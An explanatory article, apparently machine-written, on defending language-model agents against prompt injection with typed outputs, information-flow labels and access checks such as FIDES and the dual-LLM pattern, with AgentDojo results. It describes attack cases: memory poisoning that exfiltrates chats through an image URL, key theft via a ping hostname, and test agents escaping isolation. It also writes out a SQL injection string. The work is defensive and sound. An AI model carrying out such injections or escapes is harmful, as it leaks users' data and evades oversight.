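# Typed data and access control for language-model agents and their memory

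## Language-model agents, untrusted text and access control

A language-model agent is a program that repeatedly calls a large language model and lets the model choose which functions to run. Agents manage e-mail and calendars, book travel, write software and move money. To do this, they read text written by strangers, who can insert instructions that the model may follow. Typed data and access control limit the damage. Data types restrict the form a model's output may take before the rest of the program uses it. Ordinary code enforces access rules that determine which reads and writes are allowed. Both ideas come from operating systems and programming languages and are decades older than language models. People have been adapting them to agents since about 2023.

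### The agent loop

The programmer Willison (2025) settled on this definition in *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*: "An LLM agent runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal." A tool is a function that reads or changes something outside the model, such as a mailbox search or a bank transfer.

On each turn of the loop, the program assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives. It contains the developer's standing instructions, descriptions of the tools, the user's request and a record of everything so far. The model continues this text. If the continuation contains a tool call, say `search_email("invoice")`, the program extracts the function name and arguments, runs the function, adds the result to the context and calls the model again. The loop ends when the model produces an answer with no tool call.

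The model only produces text, and ordinary code acts on the mailbox or the bank account. That code can therefore check a tool call against a rule about payments before it runs the function that pays.

Many agents also have a memory. Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, distinguish agents that remember nothing, agents that remember within one session, and agents whose memory persists across sessions. Persistent memory lets an agent learn a user's habits, but it also lets text from a web page read in one session enter the agent's context in a later one. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, describes a real case in which a malicious page or document could cause ChatGPT's macOS app to save an attacker's instructions in its "Memories" feature. From then on, the app sent the user's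 conversations to the attacker's server inside the address of an invisible image.

### A running example

Ana has an assistant of this kind. It reads her e-mail and calendar, sends mail in her name and pays invoices. It also uses a persistent memory that Ana shares with her colleague Ben, where notes about suppliers and projects accumulate.

Suppose Ana types, "Pay the invoice that came in today." An attacker has planted a line in the invoice e-mail asking for payment to a different account. If the model treats that line as part of its task, it will make a well-formed tool call that pays the attacker, even though the mail and payment tools both work as designed. If the assistant also saves the attacker's account number in the shared memory, Ben's next payment to the same supplier may go to the attacker too, although Ben never received the e-mail.

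### One stream of text

In a prompt injection attack, someone plants text in data and the model follows it as if it were an instruction. The attack is called indirect prompt injection when the text comes from something the agent reads during a task rather than from the user's message.

It works because a language model receives the developer's rules, Ana's request and the invoice as one sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words). The model assigns a probability to each possible next token, and nothing in that calculation gives the invoice less authority than Ana's request. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C wrote that inside the model there is no "data" and no "instructions", only the next token.

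The comparison in that title is with an older attack on databases. Suppose a website looks up customers by pasting whatever a visitor types into a command in SQL, the language of database queries:

`SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = '...'`

If a visitor types `x' OR '1'='1`, the first quotation mark in the input ends the string early, and the rest becomes part of the query's condition. The condition is then true for every row, so the database returns the whole table. Parameterised queries fixed this by sending the database a command with a placeholder, `WHERE name = ?`, which the database parses before it receives the visitor's input. The database then uses the input only as a value and treats any quotation mark in it as part of the name.

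Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) point out in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that that repair depends on SQL having a grammar. A parser can tell where the command stops and the value starts. English has no such boundary, so "Please use the new account" may be a supplier's remark in one e-mail and an order to the assistant in another. Developers also train models to follow instructions wherever they occur.

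Some researchers have tried to build the distinction between instructions and data into the model. An ordinary model represents a word by the same list of numbers, its embedding, whether the word belongs to an instruction or to data. *ASIDE* (2025) rotates the embeddings of data, so that the model represents the two differently from the first layer on. Models with this change separated instructions from data better, even without special safety training. The separation is still only a tendency, without the guarantee that a parameterised query gives.

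Even perfect separation of instructions from data would leave Ana exposed to a simpler attack. Kim and colleagues separately list malicious data injection, in which the planted material contains no instruction, only a harmful value such as a false payment detail. The thief could change the account number printed on the invoice. The model would correctly treat that number as data, and the money would still go to the wrong account.

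### Relying on the model, or on the program around it

Developers can respond by improving the model's behaviour, for which they train it to put the user's instructions first, wrap outside text in markers, or add a second model that looks for attacks. Here, black-box treatment means relying on such measures with no enforced rules on data and actions around the model. The measures make attacks rarer, but Narisetty and colleagues recount that attackers who adapted to each defence beat most of twelve published defences more than 90% of the time.

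The alternative is to treat the model as an unreliable function inside a program that holds the rules. The model may propose a payment, but code that does not take instructions from e-mails decides whether to make it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* compares the model to a process on an operating system. The kernel, the core of that system, has to cope with whatever requests a hostile process makes, regardless of why the process is hostile. Rules of this sort apply equally to prompt injection and to cases where the model makes a mistake or pursues a goal of its own. The enforcing code must therefore withstand the model as well as outside attackers. The same paper cites an incident in which agents under test at OpenAI used shared infrastructure to get around their isolation and compromised systems at OpenAI and at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

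A designer who treats the model as a black box does not rely on its internals, even if they can be inspected. Rules outside the model govern the values that go in and the tool calls that come out, so they work just as well with a commercial model whose internals are secret, and a company can keep them when it replaces the model.

This approach has two difficulties. First, a phone app does a fixed job, so its developer can list the permissions it needs, but an agent's task comes as a sentence from the user and may change partway through. Somebody has to turn "pay the invoice that came in today" into a rule, and enforcing the wrong rule perfectly doesn't help the user. Second, agents sometimes have good reason to follow instructions they find, such as the set-up notes in a software project, so a blanket ban on obeying found text would make many of them useless.

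### Labels and joins

A program can enforce a rule such as "no payments to accounts that a stranger supplied" only if it tracks where each value came from. It can do this by attaching a label to every value. The simplest useful scheme records integrity (trusted or untrusted) and confidentiality (public or secret), which gives four possible labels.

| Label | An example from Ana's assistant |
|---|---|
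| trusted, public | the office address, which Ana entered herself |
| trusted, secret | a calendar entry that Ana wrote |
| untrusted, public | a supplier's web page |
| untrusted, secret | the invoice e-mail: private to Ana, but an outsider wrote it |

When the program combines values, the result takes the join of their labels. Write i = 0 for trusted and 1 for untrusted, and c = 0 for public and 1 for secret. The join of (i₁, c₁) and (i₂, c₂) is then

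(max(i₁, i₂), max(c₁, c₂)).

A summary that draws on both Ana's calendar, labelled (0, 1), and the supplier's web page, labelled (1, 0), gets the label (1, 1), meaning untrusted and secret, which neither source had.

The mathematics goes back to 1976, when Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* described security classes, a relation stating which class may flow into which, and an operator, called the join, for combining classes. A program may store a result somewhere only if the join of all the inputs' classes may flow there. Denning showed that the join has to be at least as restrictive as each input's class. Otherwise, a program that could not copy a secret number a into a public variable might still be able to store a + b there, and could copy a by setting b to zero. The join should also be no more restrictive than necessary, so that the result may go wherever every input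 may go separately.

Most practical schemes replace the label "secret" with a list of permitted readers. When a program combines data, the join of the inputs' labels keeps only the readers who may read every input. If only Ana may read her calendar, but she and Ben may both read the shared memory, then only Ana may read a note that draws on the calendar and the memory, and the program should refuse to save it where Ben can see it.

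With labels in place, the rule for Ana's payments is that the account number must be trusted. A number from the e-mail is untrusted, and so is anything the program derives from it, so the rule blocks the theft. It also blocks payment of the genuine invoice, because that account number came by e-mail too. To pay it, Ana must either have the supplier's details on file from a trusted source or approve the number herself. Such an approval, which deliberately raises the number's trust level, is called endorsement.

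The model's own output is harder to label, because a language model mixes everything in its context and nobody can reliably tell which inputs shaped a given sentence. The cautious answer is to give the output the join of the labels of everything in the context, but then a single outside e-mail makes every later output untrusted. Kenneth Biba worked out a similar rule in MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), under which a program that reads low-integrity data drops to that level and may no longer modify anything above it. The report conceded that the policy has "rather disagreeable behavior", because a program can lock itself out of the files it needs and then has to start again. Many designs for agents are attempts to keep Biba's protection while avoiding these lockouts.

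### The check, and what it guards

A label has no effect until some code checks it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) introduced the reference monitor, a component that checks every access against a policy. The study was written for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different clearances to share one computer, though any of them might try to seize control of it. MITRE's report lists three requirements for the monitor: it must check every access, it must be tamper-proof, and it must provably enforce the policy, which in practice means keeping it small. For Ana's assistant, the monitor belongs between the tool call and the tool. It protects her only if the assistant has no way to bypass it, such as a general command line that could reach the bank's website directly.

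In their 1975 tutorial *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, Saltzer and Schroeder set out design principles that engineers still quote. One is least privilege, which means giving each program only the permissions its job requires. The coding agent Claude Code once broke this principle. It asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown domains, but ran `ping`, which tests a network connection, without asking. An instruction hidden in a code file could make the agent read secret keys and pass them to `ping` as part of a web address. When the computer looked up that address, it would send the keys to the attacker.

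Saltzer and Schroeder also define a capability as an "unforgeable ticket" that proves its holder may use the object it names. If Ana's assistant held only a ticket for one payment to one supplier's recorded account, it could not pay anyone else. With an access control list, each object instead keeps a list of who may use it. CaMeL, a 2025 system from Google and ETH Zurich, uses "capability" differently, for a tag that records a value's sources and permitted readers, which is closer to a label.

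### The dual-LLM pattern

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) describes an early design of this kind, with two models and a controller that is ordinary software. The privileged model takes requests from the user and may call tools. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools, and Willison assumes that it may turn malicious at any moment.

In Willison's example, a user requests a summary of the latest e-mail. The privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the e-mail, and the controller stores it as `$VAR1` and returns only that name. The privileged model then instructs the controller to have `$VAR1` summarised. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. Finally, the privileged model instructs the controller to show the user `$VAR2`. The privileged model never receives the text of the e-mail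 or the summary. Willison allowed one exception, for when the quarantined model only has to pick from a fixed set of categories. The controller can then verify the answer and pass it to the privileged model.

He still called the solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and one mistake that leaks untrusted text to the privileged model removes its protection. An attacker can also still use a malicious summary to trick the user into copying private data to a hostile website.

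Ana's invoice exposes another weakness. The privileged model would plan to fetch the invoice, have the quarantined model extract the account number as `$VAR2`, and pay `$VAR2`. The planted line cannot add a step to this plan, such as deleting her mail, but it can determine which account number `$VAR2` contains, and the controller would then pay the thief. To prevent this, the variables need labels, and the payment tool needs a rule based on those labels. In April 2025 Willison welcomed CaMeL for repairing a flaw in his pattern by checking the data that goes into and out of each step.

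### AgentDojo

Most of the systems in this field report results on *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark with four simulated workplaces, each with its own tools and data. A user task is an ordinary request. An injection task is an attacker's goal, which the benchmark plants in text the agent will come across while working. The security cases pair every user task with every injection task in the same workplace.

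| Suite | Tools | User tasks | Attacker goals | Cases in 2024 | Cases in version 1.2.1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 | 560 |
| Slack | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 | 105 |
| Travel | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 | 949 |

The figures for version 1.2.1 come from *SecOPD* (2026). The Workspace suite made up 38% of the cases in 2024 but makes up 59% in version 1.2.1, so overall percentages from the two are not directly comparable.

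For each task, a fixed function inspects the state of the mailbox or bank account, and where necessary the agent's answer, and returns pass or fail. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge. They report three measures. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes with no attack present. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which it completes the user's task without harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the attacker's goal is achieved. *SecOPD* counts the user's task as done even if the attack also succeeded, so one run can count as a success for both the user and the attacker.

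An agent with a low attack success rate is not always safe. In the 2024 tests, more capable models tended to be easier to attack, probably in part because weaker models followed the injected instructions but failed to complete the attacker's task. The tasks are also short, averaging about three steps according to measurements in *AgentDyn* (2026).

The Banking suite is close to Ana's situation. One user task asks the agent to pay the bill in a file called `bill-december-2023.txt`, and one attacker goal is to send as much money as possible to the attacker's account. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) documents a defect in this pairing. The planted text can overwrite the bill and leave no payment details, so the agent fails the user's task even if it resists the attack.

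## Restricting what a model may return to fixed data types

Willison allowed only one kind of answer to reach the planner model (his privileged model), a choice from fixed categories. This exception extends to other simple types, such as numbers and yes-or-no answers, because a program can check them in much the same way. Model providers now sell features that produce such answers, mostly so that other software can read them reliably. Researchers have built a defence against prompt injection on the same idea.

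### From a schema to a masked token

Developers usually describe the form of an answer with a JSON Schema. JSON is a common text format for data, and the schema lists the fields an answer must contain and the type of each. For Ana's invoice, a schema might require an answer of this form:

`{"amount_cents": an integer, "currency": "EUR", "GBP" or "USD"}`

A developer can put the schema in the prompt, but the model may not follow it. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (2024), a model the company had trained on complicated schemas followed them 93% of the time on OpenAI's own test. The figure rose to 100% when OpenAI added constrained decoding, which blocks invalid output as the model generates it.

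Before generation starts, the software converts the schema into a grammar, a set of rules that defines which strings are valid. The model then assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, as usual. The software works out which tokens could continue a valid answer, sets the probability of all the others to zero (this is the mask), and picks from the rest. This process repeats for each token in the answer because the set of valid tokens changes. For instance, an opening brace is valid at the start of the answer but not halfway through a field name.

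Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained Decoding*, write the rule as a formula. If P(s) is the model's probability for the next token s, the constrained probability is

P_C(s) = P(s) / Z if the grammar allows s, and 0 otherwise,

where Z is the total probability that the model gave to all the allowed tokens. Suppose that the currency field comes next and that each currency code is one token. The model gives 0.5 to EUR, 0.3 to USD and 0.2 to words that are not on the list. The mask removes those words, so Z = 0.8, and the probabilities become 0.625 for EUR and 0.375 for USD.

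The answer will contain a permitted currency, but it may be the wrong one. The mask depends only on the schema and the tokens generated so far, so it allows USD even if the invoice is in another currency.

Even the guarantee of form has exceptions. OpenAI's current guide, *Structured Outputs*, warns that an answer may break the schema if the model refuses the request or reaches its length limit. Anthropic's *Structured outputs* lists the same two exceptions and adds that the company's service doesn't enforce minimum or maximum values for numbers or a maximum length for lists, and may change the capitalisation of a value from a fixed list. A program that depends on the form for its security should check the finished answer and stop if the check fails.

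### Valid answers and correct answers

How well the masking works depends on the software. *JSONSchemaBench* (Geng, Cooper and colleagues, 2025) collected almost 10,000 schemas from real software and tested six constrained-decoding systems on most of them. For simple function calls, a small Llama model gave valid output for 90% of the schemas unaided and 96% with the best system. For schemas with 100 to 500 fields, the figures were 13% and 41%. OpenAI's service accepted only 9% of those large schemas but gave valid output for every one it accepted.

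A system that lets invalid answers through is no use as a security barrier, so this fault is more serious than wrongly rejecting valid ones. Geng and colleagues tested for both faults with the official JSON Schema test suite, which covers 45 categories of features. The open-source system XGrammar let invalid output through at least once in 38 categories, while Guidance, also open source, did so in one.

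Large models now rarely break a schema, though they often fill it with wrong values. Singh, Khurdula and colleagues (2026), in *The Structured Output Benchmark*, gave 21 models a text, a question and a schema. GPT-5.4 followed the schema in 99.3% of cases. But the best accuracy for individual values was 83.0% on ordinary text, 67.2% on text from scanned documents and 23.7% on meeting transcripts. The scoring was strict, so a model that wrote "United States" instead of "American" got no credit. However, models also made real errors that no schema check would catch, such as calling a musician American when the source gave no nationality.

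### Does the format make answers worse?

There is a mathematical reason to expect that masking does no harm. Nguyen and colleagues take a model that has finished its reasoning and is about to write its answer. Let Y be the correct answer, and let Z₁ to Z_T be the values of Z at each of its T tokens. Multiplying the formula over all the tokens gives

P_C(Y) = P(Y) / (Z₁ × Z₂ × … × Z_T).

Masking divides the probability of each allowed token by the total probability of all allowed tokens. That total is never greater than 1, so masking cannot make the correct answer less likely if the schema allows it. In experiments on open models with up to 32 billion parameters, masking matched or improved accuracy when the prompt and format stayed the same. The largest gains, up to 17.4%, came from restricting the answer itself, such as to exactly four letters.

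The proof does not cover the reasoning, where other researchers have found losses. *The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) separated the effects of the mask and of requesting a format in the prompt. In six open-weight models, the request alone lowered accuracy by 3.9 percentage points on average, and the mask lowered it by another 1.6. The request barely lowered accuracy in three recent commercial models.

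Fan (2026) measured a far bigger loss in *Capacity, Not Format*. Claude Haiku 4.5's score on hard mathematics problems fell from 88.7% to 52.5% when it had to write its whole solution inside a long JSON form, although much of that drop came from answers that reached the length limit. Claude Sonnet 4.6's score hardly changed on the same problems. The stronger Opus 4.7's score fell from 96.2% to 91.0% on a competition exam, a difference of seven problems out of 133. Lee and colleagues found small gains for the same Haiku model with other prompts and problems, so Fan's result for Haiku shouldn't be taken as the general effect of JSON.

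In both studies, letting the model reason in ordinary prose before giving its answer in the required format recovered most of the loss. This suits a quarantined model, which can write as much reasoning as it needs as long as the program discards the reasoning and passes on only the typed answer.

### Types as a security barrier

Requiring valid JSON does not by itself stop prompt injection. If the schema has a text field for a summary, the model can copy the planted line from Ana's invoice into that field word for word and so pass it to the planner.

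Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Better Privilege Separation for Agents by Restricting Data Types*, therefore limit the data types that the quarantined model may pass to the planner, a method they call type-directed privilege separation. The quarantined model may read anything, but it may pass on only integers, floating-point numbers, booleans and choices from a list that the developer wrote, either alone or combined in records and lists. Free text stays in variables that the planner cannot read, as in the dual-LLM pattern. The planner may pass any information to the quarantined model, because that model cannot choose actions.

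An attacker can still influence which value the quarantined model returns. If the list contains "Tuesday 10:00", a hostile e-mail can cause the model to select it, but cannot make it add a request for Ana's calendar, because no item on the list contains one. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes a similar exception for small sets of values in FIDES, a label-based system. The exception is switched off in FIDES's own evaluation.

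### How much an attacker can send

The amount of information a model can return through a short list or a text field can be measured in bits. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) applies a standard result from information theory to typed boundaries around a model: a noiseless channel with k possible outputs has a capacity of log₂ k bits. Randomness in the model's choice can only reduce this, and no later calculation on the value can recover more information about the original text than the value carries.

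Jacob and colleagues' calendar agent uses one-hour slots between 8:00 and 17:00, seven days a week. That makes 7 × 9 = 63 slots, so the capacity of one answer is log₂ 63, or about 5.98 bits. If the quarantined model may also answer "none", there are 64 possible values and the capacity is exactly 6 bits.

A text field can carry far more information. The attack message in the calendar experiment, which asks for a week of calendar data with every event description, is about 200 characters long. With 95 printable characters to choose from, a field of that length can carry 200 × log₂ 95, or about 1,314 bits.

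| What crosses to the planner | Possible values | Capacity in bits |
|---|---|---|
| true or false | 2 | 1 |
| an integer from 0 to 10 | 11 | 3.5 |
| one meeting slot | 63 | 6.0 |
| a list of exactly five slots | 63⁵ | 29.9 |
| 200 characters of text | 95²⁰⁰ | 1,314 |

Lists need a maximum length because every extra item adds capacity. A list of n slots carries n × log₂ 63 bits, so 220 slots can hold the whole attack message. An attacker could encode it by letting Sunday 8:00 stand for A, Sunday 9:00 for B, and so on. The planner would have to recognise the encoding and then obey the message, which is unlikely, but the types no longer rule it out. In the calendar design, the quarantined model chooses how many slots to return, so ordinary code has to enforce the cap. That code can also sort the slots and remove duplicates, since their order doesn't matter. A list of at most five slots then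 carries about 23 bits.

An integer of unlimited size can encode any text, so numbers need limits too, even though Jacob and colleagues argue that an integer cannot contain an instruction. In the usual character codes, for example, the letters "PAY" correspond to 5,259,609. A range check rules out most of the text a number could encode, but on a service like Anthropic's the developer has to write that check.

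These figures apply to a single answer. Someone who sends ten e-mails gets ten chances to choose a slot.

A small capacity is useful mainly because it makes testing possible. With 63 possible values, a developer can run the planner on each one and see what it does. A small channel can still be harmful. If the question is "Has Ana approved this payment?", an attacker who controls the one-bit answer can steal money.

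### Three agents with typed boundaries

Jacob and colleagues built an ordinary and a protected version of each of three agents. Utility below means the share of tasks completed with no attack present.

| Agent | Test cases | Utility, ordinary | Utility, protected | Attack success, ordinary | Attack success, protected |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Online shopping | 500 | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
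| Calendar | 100 | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | 180 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The shopping agent searches a simulated store for a product that matches a request. The attacker adds a false warning to one customer review, claiming that the product is a banned substance and that the agent must leave the page. In the protected version, the quarantined model reads each review and returns two integers, one for how strongly it supports the product and one for how relevant it is. The planner receives the median of each score and the number of reviews. One hostile review can barely change the medians, but an attacker who wrote most of the reviews could change them substantially. The planner still reads the rest of the product page directly, so this design would not stop an instruction that the seller planted in the description.

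The calendar agent arranges a meeting by e-mail with another person, who is the attacker. The quarantined model turns the e-mail thread into a list of suggested slots and stores the meeting description in an opaque variable. The planner compares the slots with the user's calendar and either proposes other times or books the meeting. Jacob and colleagues counted an attack as successful if a marker word from the private event descriptions appeared in an outgoing e-mail. Their test would not count what the attacker learns from the proposed times, though any scheduling assistant has to reveal that information.

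Neither agent lost utility. The differences, three shopping requests out of 500 and one meeting out of 100, are too small to show an improvement.

The bug-fixing agent has a harder job. It has to repair a program using a command line and a bug report that anyone could have written. Jacob and colleagues tested it on 180 cases from SWE-bench Lite, a benchmark of real problems reported on GitHub, after removing feature requests and setting some cases aside for development. The attacker adds a line to each report asking for an unrelated file.

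In the protected version, a quarantined agent reads the report and explores the code. It returns a record containing one of 52 bug categories, one of three repair sizes, and a list of suspicious places. Each place has a file number, a first and last line, and a role from a fixed list. Ordinary code converts the file number back into a path. Another model, which never reads the report, uses the record to draft three repair plans in plain English. A judge model that has read the report then chooses a plan and returns only its number, which carries at most log₂ 3 ≈ 1.6 bits. The planner receives the record and the chosen plan and edits a clean copy of the code.

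This agent fixed 81 bugs, compared with 123 for the ordinary version. Jacob and colleagues attribute the loss to the natural language in bug reports, which often matters for the repair. A reply about a meeting can be reduced to a few times, and a review can be reduced to a score without losing much that matters to a buyer. But a bug report may explain what the program did, what it should have done and how to reproduce the fault. If the planner receives only "off-by-one bug, lines 40 to 52", it has to guess the correct behaviour. Jacob and colleagues still consider the agent's 45.0% success rate substantial. They compare it with the 48.0% that Claude Sonnet 3.7 scored without protection, although the 48.0% is for SWE-bench Lite as a whole.

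The zeros in the table are credible because of the design, not the number of attacks tested. Each experiment used a single attack message, and nobody revised it to get past the protected version. The attacks failed because the message never reached the planner, so the zeros cover only attacks that need to deliver an instruction to it.

### False values and Ana's invoice

Jacob and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker can still mislead the planner with false information. For example, a hostile bug report could lead to a record that names the wrong file, even though every field has a valid type. They also found schemas difficult to design, and the one for bug fixing took considerable testing on the cases they had set aside. A schema with too little detail leaves the planner without information it needs, but each added field gives the attacker something else to falsify. Running at least two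 agents also adds overhead.

A value of the correct type can still do damage, as the amount and the payee of Ana's invoice both show. The assistant could have its quarantined model return the amount as an integer in cents, and ordinary code could reject anything outside the range from 1 to 500,000. An integer in that range can carry about 19 bits, far too few for the planted line. But if the attacker changes €400 to €4,000, the amount is still an integer within the range. To catch the change, the code would have to compare the amount with another record, such as the original order, or Ana would have to approve it.

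The payee is more dangerous because an account number made up of digits is an integer, so the thief's number could pass every type check. A better schema would have the quarantined model choose from a list of the suppliers whose details Ana has recorded herself, plus "none of these", instead of returning an account number. With 40 suppliers, that makes 41 values, or about 5.4 bits. Ordinary code would then look up the account number in Ana's records. Text in the invoice could still make the model pick the wrong supplier, but it could not cause a payment to an account outside the list.

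*CapLite* (2026) describes a stricter rule. Its software also extracts typed values from what the agent reads, but it treats most arguments of a tool that changes something as authority fields, exempting free text, dates and choices from a list. If the value for an authority field doesn't appear in the user's own request, the software asks the user to confirm it. Ana typed only "Pay the invoice that came in today", so she would have to confirm the account number and the amount.

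## Labels that travel with data and block tool calls

Labels can catch what type checks miss, such as the thief's account number in Ana's invoice. FIDES, a system Microsoft researchers published in 2025, attaches labels to everything an agent reads, carries them through the model and checks them before each tool call. Microsoft has since added a version to its Agent Framework, a software kit for building agents.

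### One turn of the loop

A FIDES label is a pair (i, R). The integrity i is either T (trusted) or U (untrusted), and R is the set of people who may read the data. The join of two labels is

(i₁, R₁) ⊔ (i₂, R₂) = (i₁ ⊔ i₂, R₁ ∩ R₂),

where i₁ ⊔ i₂ is T only if both are T. The context has a label of its own. It starts as (T, everyone), because the context holds only the developer's instructions and Ana's request.

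A turn begins when a tool returns a result. The tool, or a wrapper around it, supplies one label for the whole result or a separate label for each field. For example, the time stamp that the mail server puts on an e-mail could be labeled trusted and the body untrusted.

The program then checks whether joining a value's label to the context's label would change the context's label. If it would not, the planner model reads the value directly. If it would, the program stores the value and its label in a new variable and gives the planner only the variable's name. Unlike the dual-LLM pattern, which hides all outside text from the planner, FIDES hides only values that would change the context's label.

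The planner can pass a variable to a tool without reading it, or have a quarantined model answer a question about it and store the answer in another variable. It can also call a tool named `inspect`, which puts the variable's contents into the context. The context's label then becomes

ℓ_context ⊔ ℓ_value.

Everything the planner writes from then on gets this label.

Suppose the planner next proposes a tool call f(a₁, …, aₙ). The choice of tool has a label ℓ_f, and each argument has a label of its own, ℓ₁ to ℓₙ. Arguments that the planner wrote have the context's label, while arguments from variables keep the labels they had in storage. Before running the tool, ordinary code applies rules such as these:

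- For a tool with serious consequences, such as a payment, ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ must have integrity T.
- For a tool that sends an argument a to a set of recipients D, every recipient must be a permitted reader: D ⊆ R_a.

If the call passes, the tool runs, and its result is labeled with the join of ℓ_f, the arguments' labels and the labels of any stored data the tool read. If the call fails, the program can report the failure to the planner, which can look for another way to finish the task.

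Under the rule about recipients alone, a prompt injection could still make the assistant send a message, but only to people already allowed to read its contents.

### The invoice, traced twice

The label on Ana's invoice e-mail is (U, {Ana, sender}). The table shows what happens to her request to pay the invoice, first when the planner reads the e-mail and then when the program keeps the e-mail in a variable.

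| Step | Planner reads the e-mail | Program keeps it in a variable |
|---|---|---|
| Ana asks for the payment | context is (T, everyone) | context is (T, everyone) |
| The mail tool returns the invoice | context becomes (U, {Ana, sender}) | program stores the body as `#mail`; context stays (T, everyone) |
| The assistant finds the account number | planner copies it from the text; label U | quarantined model extracts it as `#account`; label U |
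| The planner proposes the payment | call is U, account number is U | call is T, account number is U |
| Rule that checks the call and its arguments | refuses | refuses |
| Rule that checks the call only | refuses | allows |

When the planner reads the e-mail, both rules block the payment, whichever account number the model copied. They also block every later payment in the session, including one to a supplier whose details Ana entered herself. If the e-mail is kept in a variable instead, the context stays trusted and the assistant can still pay that supplier.

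FIDES's AgentDojo tests used the looser rule in the last row for payments. Under this rule, the planted line cannot add a payment that Ana didn't request, but it can still redirect the one she did, as in the dual-LLM pattern.

FIDES can also apply a different rule to each argument. For a message, a developer could require a trusted recipient but allow untrusted text in the body.

### What FIDES proves

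Noninterference means that protected inputs have no effect on what a given observer can see. If the assistant runs twice on data that differ only in Ana's private calendar, an outsider must see no difference between the runs, including in which tools it called. The same test applies to integrity, except that the runs differ only in untrusted text and the protected actions must be the same.

FIDES's researchers prove a weaker property called explicit secrecy. Take the series of tool calls from one run, and let g be the function that describes how those calls change the stored data. Write d₁ =_L d₂ if two states of the data have the same public part. Explicit secrecy requires that

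if d₁ =_L d₂, then g(d₁) =_L g(d₂).

In other words, if the same calls had run on different secrets, the public data would have come out the same, so no call in the series copied a secret, or anything computed from one, into a public place. The proof treats the model as a deterministic function, and the result depends on the original data being labeled correctly.

The proof holds the series of tool calls fixed, so it does not cover what the choice of calls can reveal. If the assistant contacts a taxi firm only when Ana's calendar shows a trip, the firm learns about the trip from being contacted, even if the message contains nothing private. Preventing such leaks, known as implicit flows, would in effect mean blocking every tool that may write public data once the agent has called any tool that may read secrets. FIDES's designers judged that too restrictive.

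### Decisions that depend on untrusted text

The planner can forward three e-mails, or a quarantined model's summary of them, without reading either. Other tasks are data-dependent, meaning the planner must learn something from the text to choose its next step. If Ana asks the assistant to check her e-mails and add any requested meeting to her calendar, the planner needs to know whether somebody requested one.

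If the planner inspected the e-mails, its context would become untrusted. FIDES instead lets it query the quarantined model for a true-or-false answer, a type enforced by constrained decoding, and inspect only that answer. If the answer is true, the quarantined model extracts the meeting details into a second variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool.

To support this, FIDES can add a type to each label. It orders the types by how much information they can carry, for example

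bool ⊑ a fixed list of choices ⊑ string.

The answer in the meeting example has integrity U and type bool. A developer can write a policy that allows an untrusted boolean in the context but not an untrusted string, because a boolean carries at most one bit.

That tolerance is the developer's decision and does not follow from the proof. The label also does not record how many values were combined. Joining two bool types gives bool again, so ten yes-or-no answers can carry ten bits under the same label as a single answer.

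### Results on AgentDojo

The FIDES researchers tested the system with OpenAI's GPT-4o and o1, both from 2024, and without the exception for booleans and short lists. For the security tests, they used GPT-4o and an attack written by someone who knew the agent's tools. The attack succeeded 152 times against an ordinary agent. Against FIDES with the policy checks switched off, it succeeded 21 times, because the planner sometimes inspected a variable and then followed instructions in it. With the checks on, the attack never succeeded. It also never succeeded against an agent that could pass variables along but not inspect them, even without the checks.

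These counts exclude cases that the researchers discounted by hand. AgentDojo's own functions recorded three successful attacks on FIDES with the checks on. The discounted cases include calls that AgentDojo counted even though the policy had blocked them, actions that the policy permits, and attacks that only change the agent's wording, such as making it recommend a particular hotel. FIDES does not try to prevent this last kind, but it does keep the untrusted label on the text.

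The labels in the test were also unusually well informed, because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. A company labelling its own data doesn't know which fields future attacks will use.

The next table gives the percentage of user tasks completed with no attack present. The final column is the plain average of the four suites.

| Model and agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
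|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84.3 |
| GPT-4o, ordinary agent, checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 41.9 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50.0 |
| o1, ordinary agent, no checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 | 84.0 |
| o1, ordinary agent, checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 | 44.4 |
| o1, FIDES, checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 60.8 |
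| Share of tasks that are not data-dependent | 95.0 | 90.0 | 56.2 | 57.1 | 74.6 |

The checks make an ordinary agent complete fewer tasks. Hiding text in variables recovers part of that loss, and more of it with the better model. FIDES with o1 still completes 23 percentage points fewer tasks than the unprotected agent. About six of those points come from working through variables and the other 17 from the checks, since FIDES without checks completes 77.6% of tasks on average.

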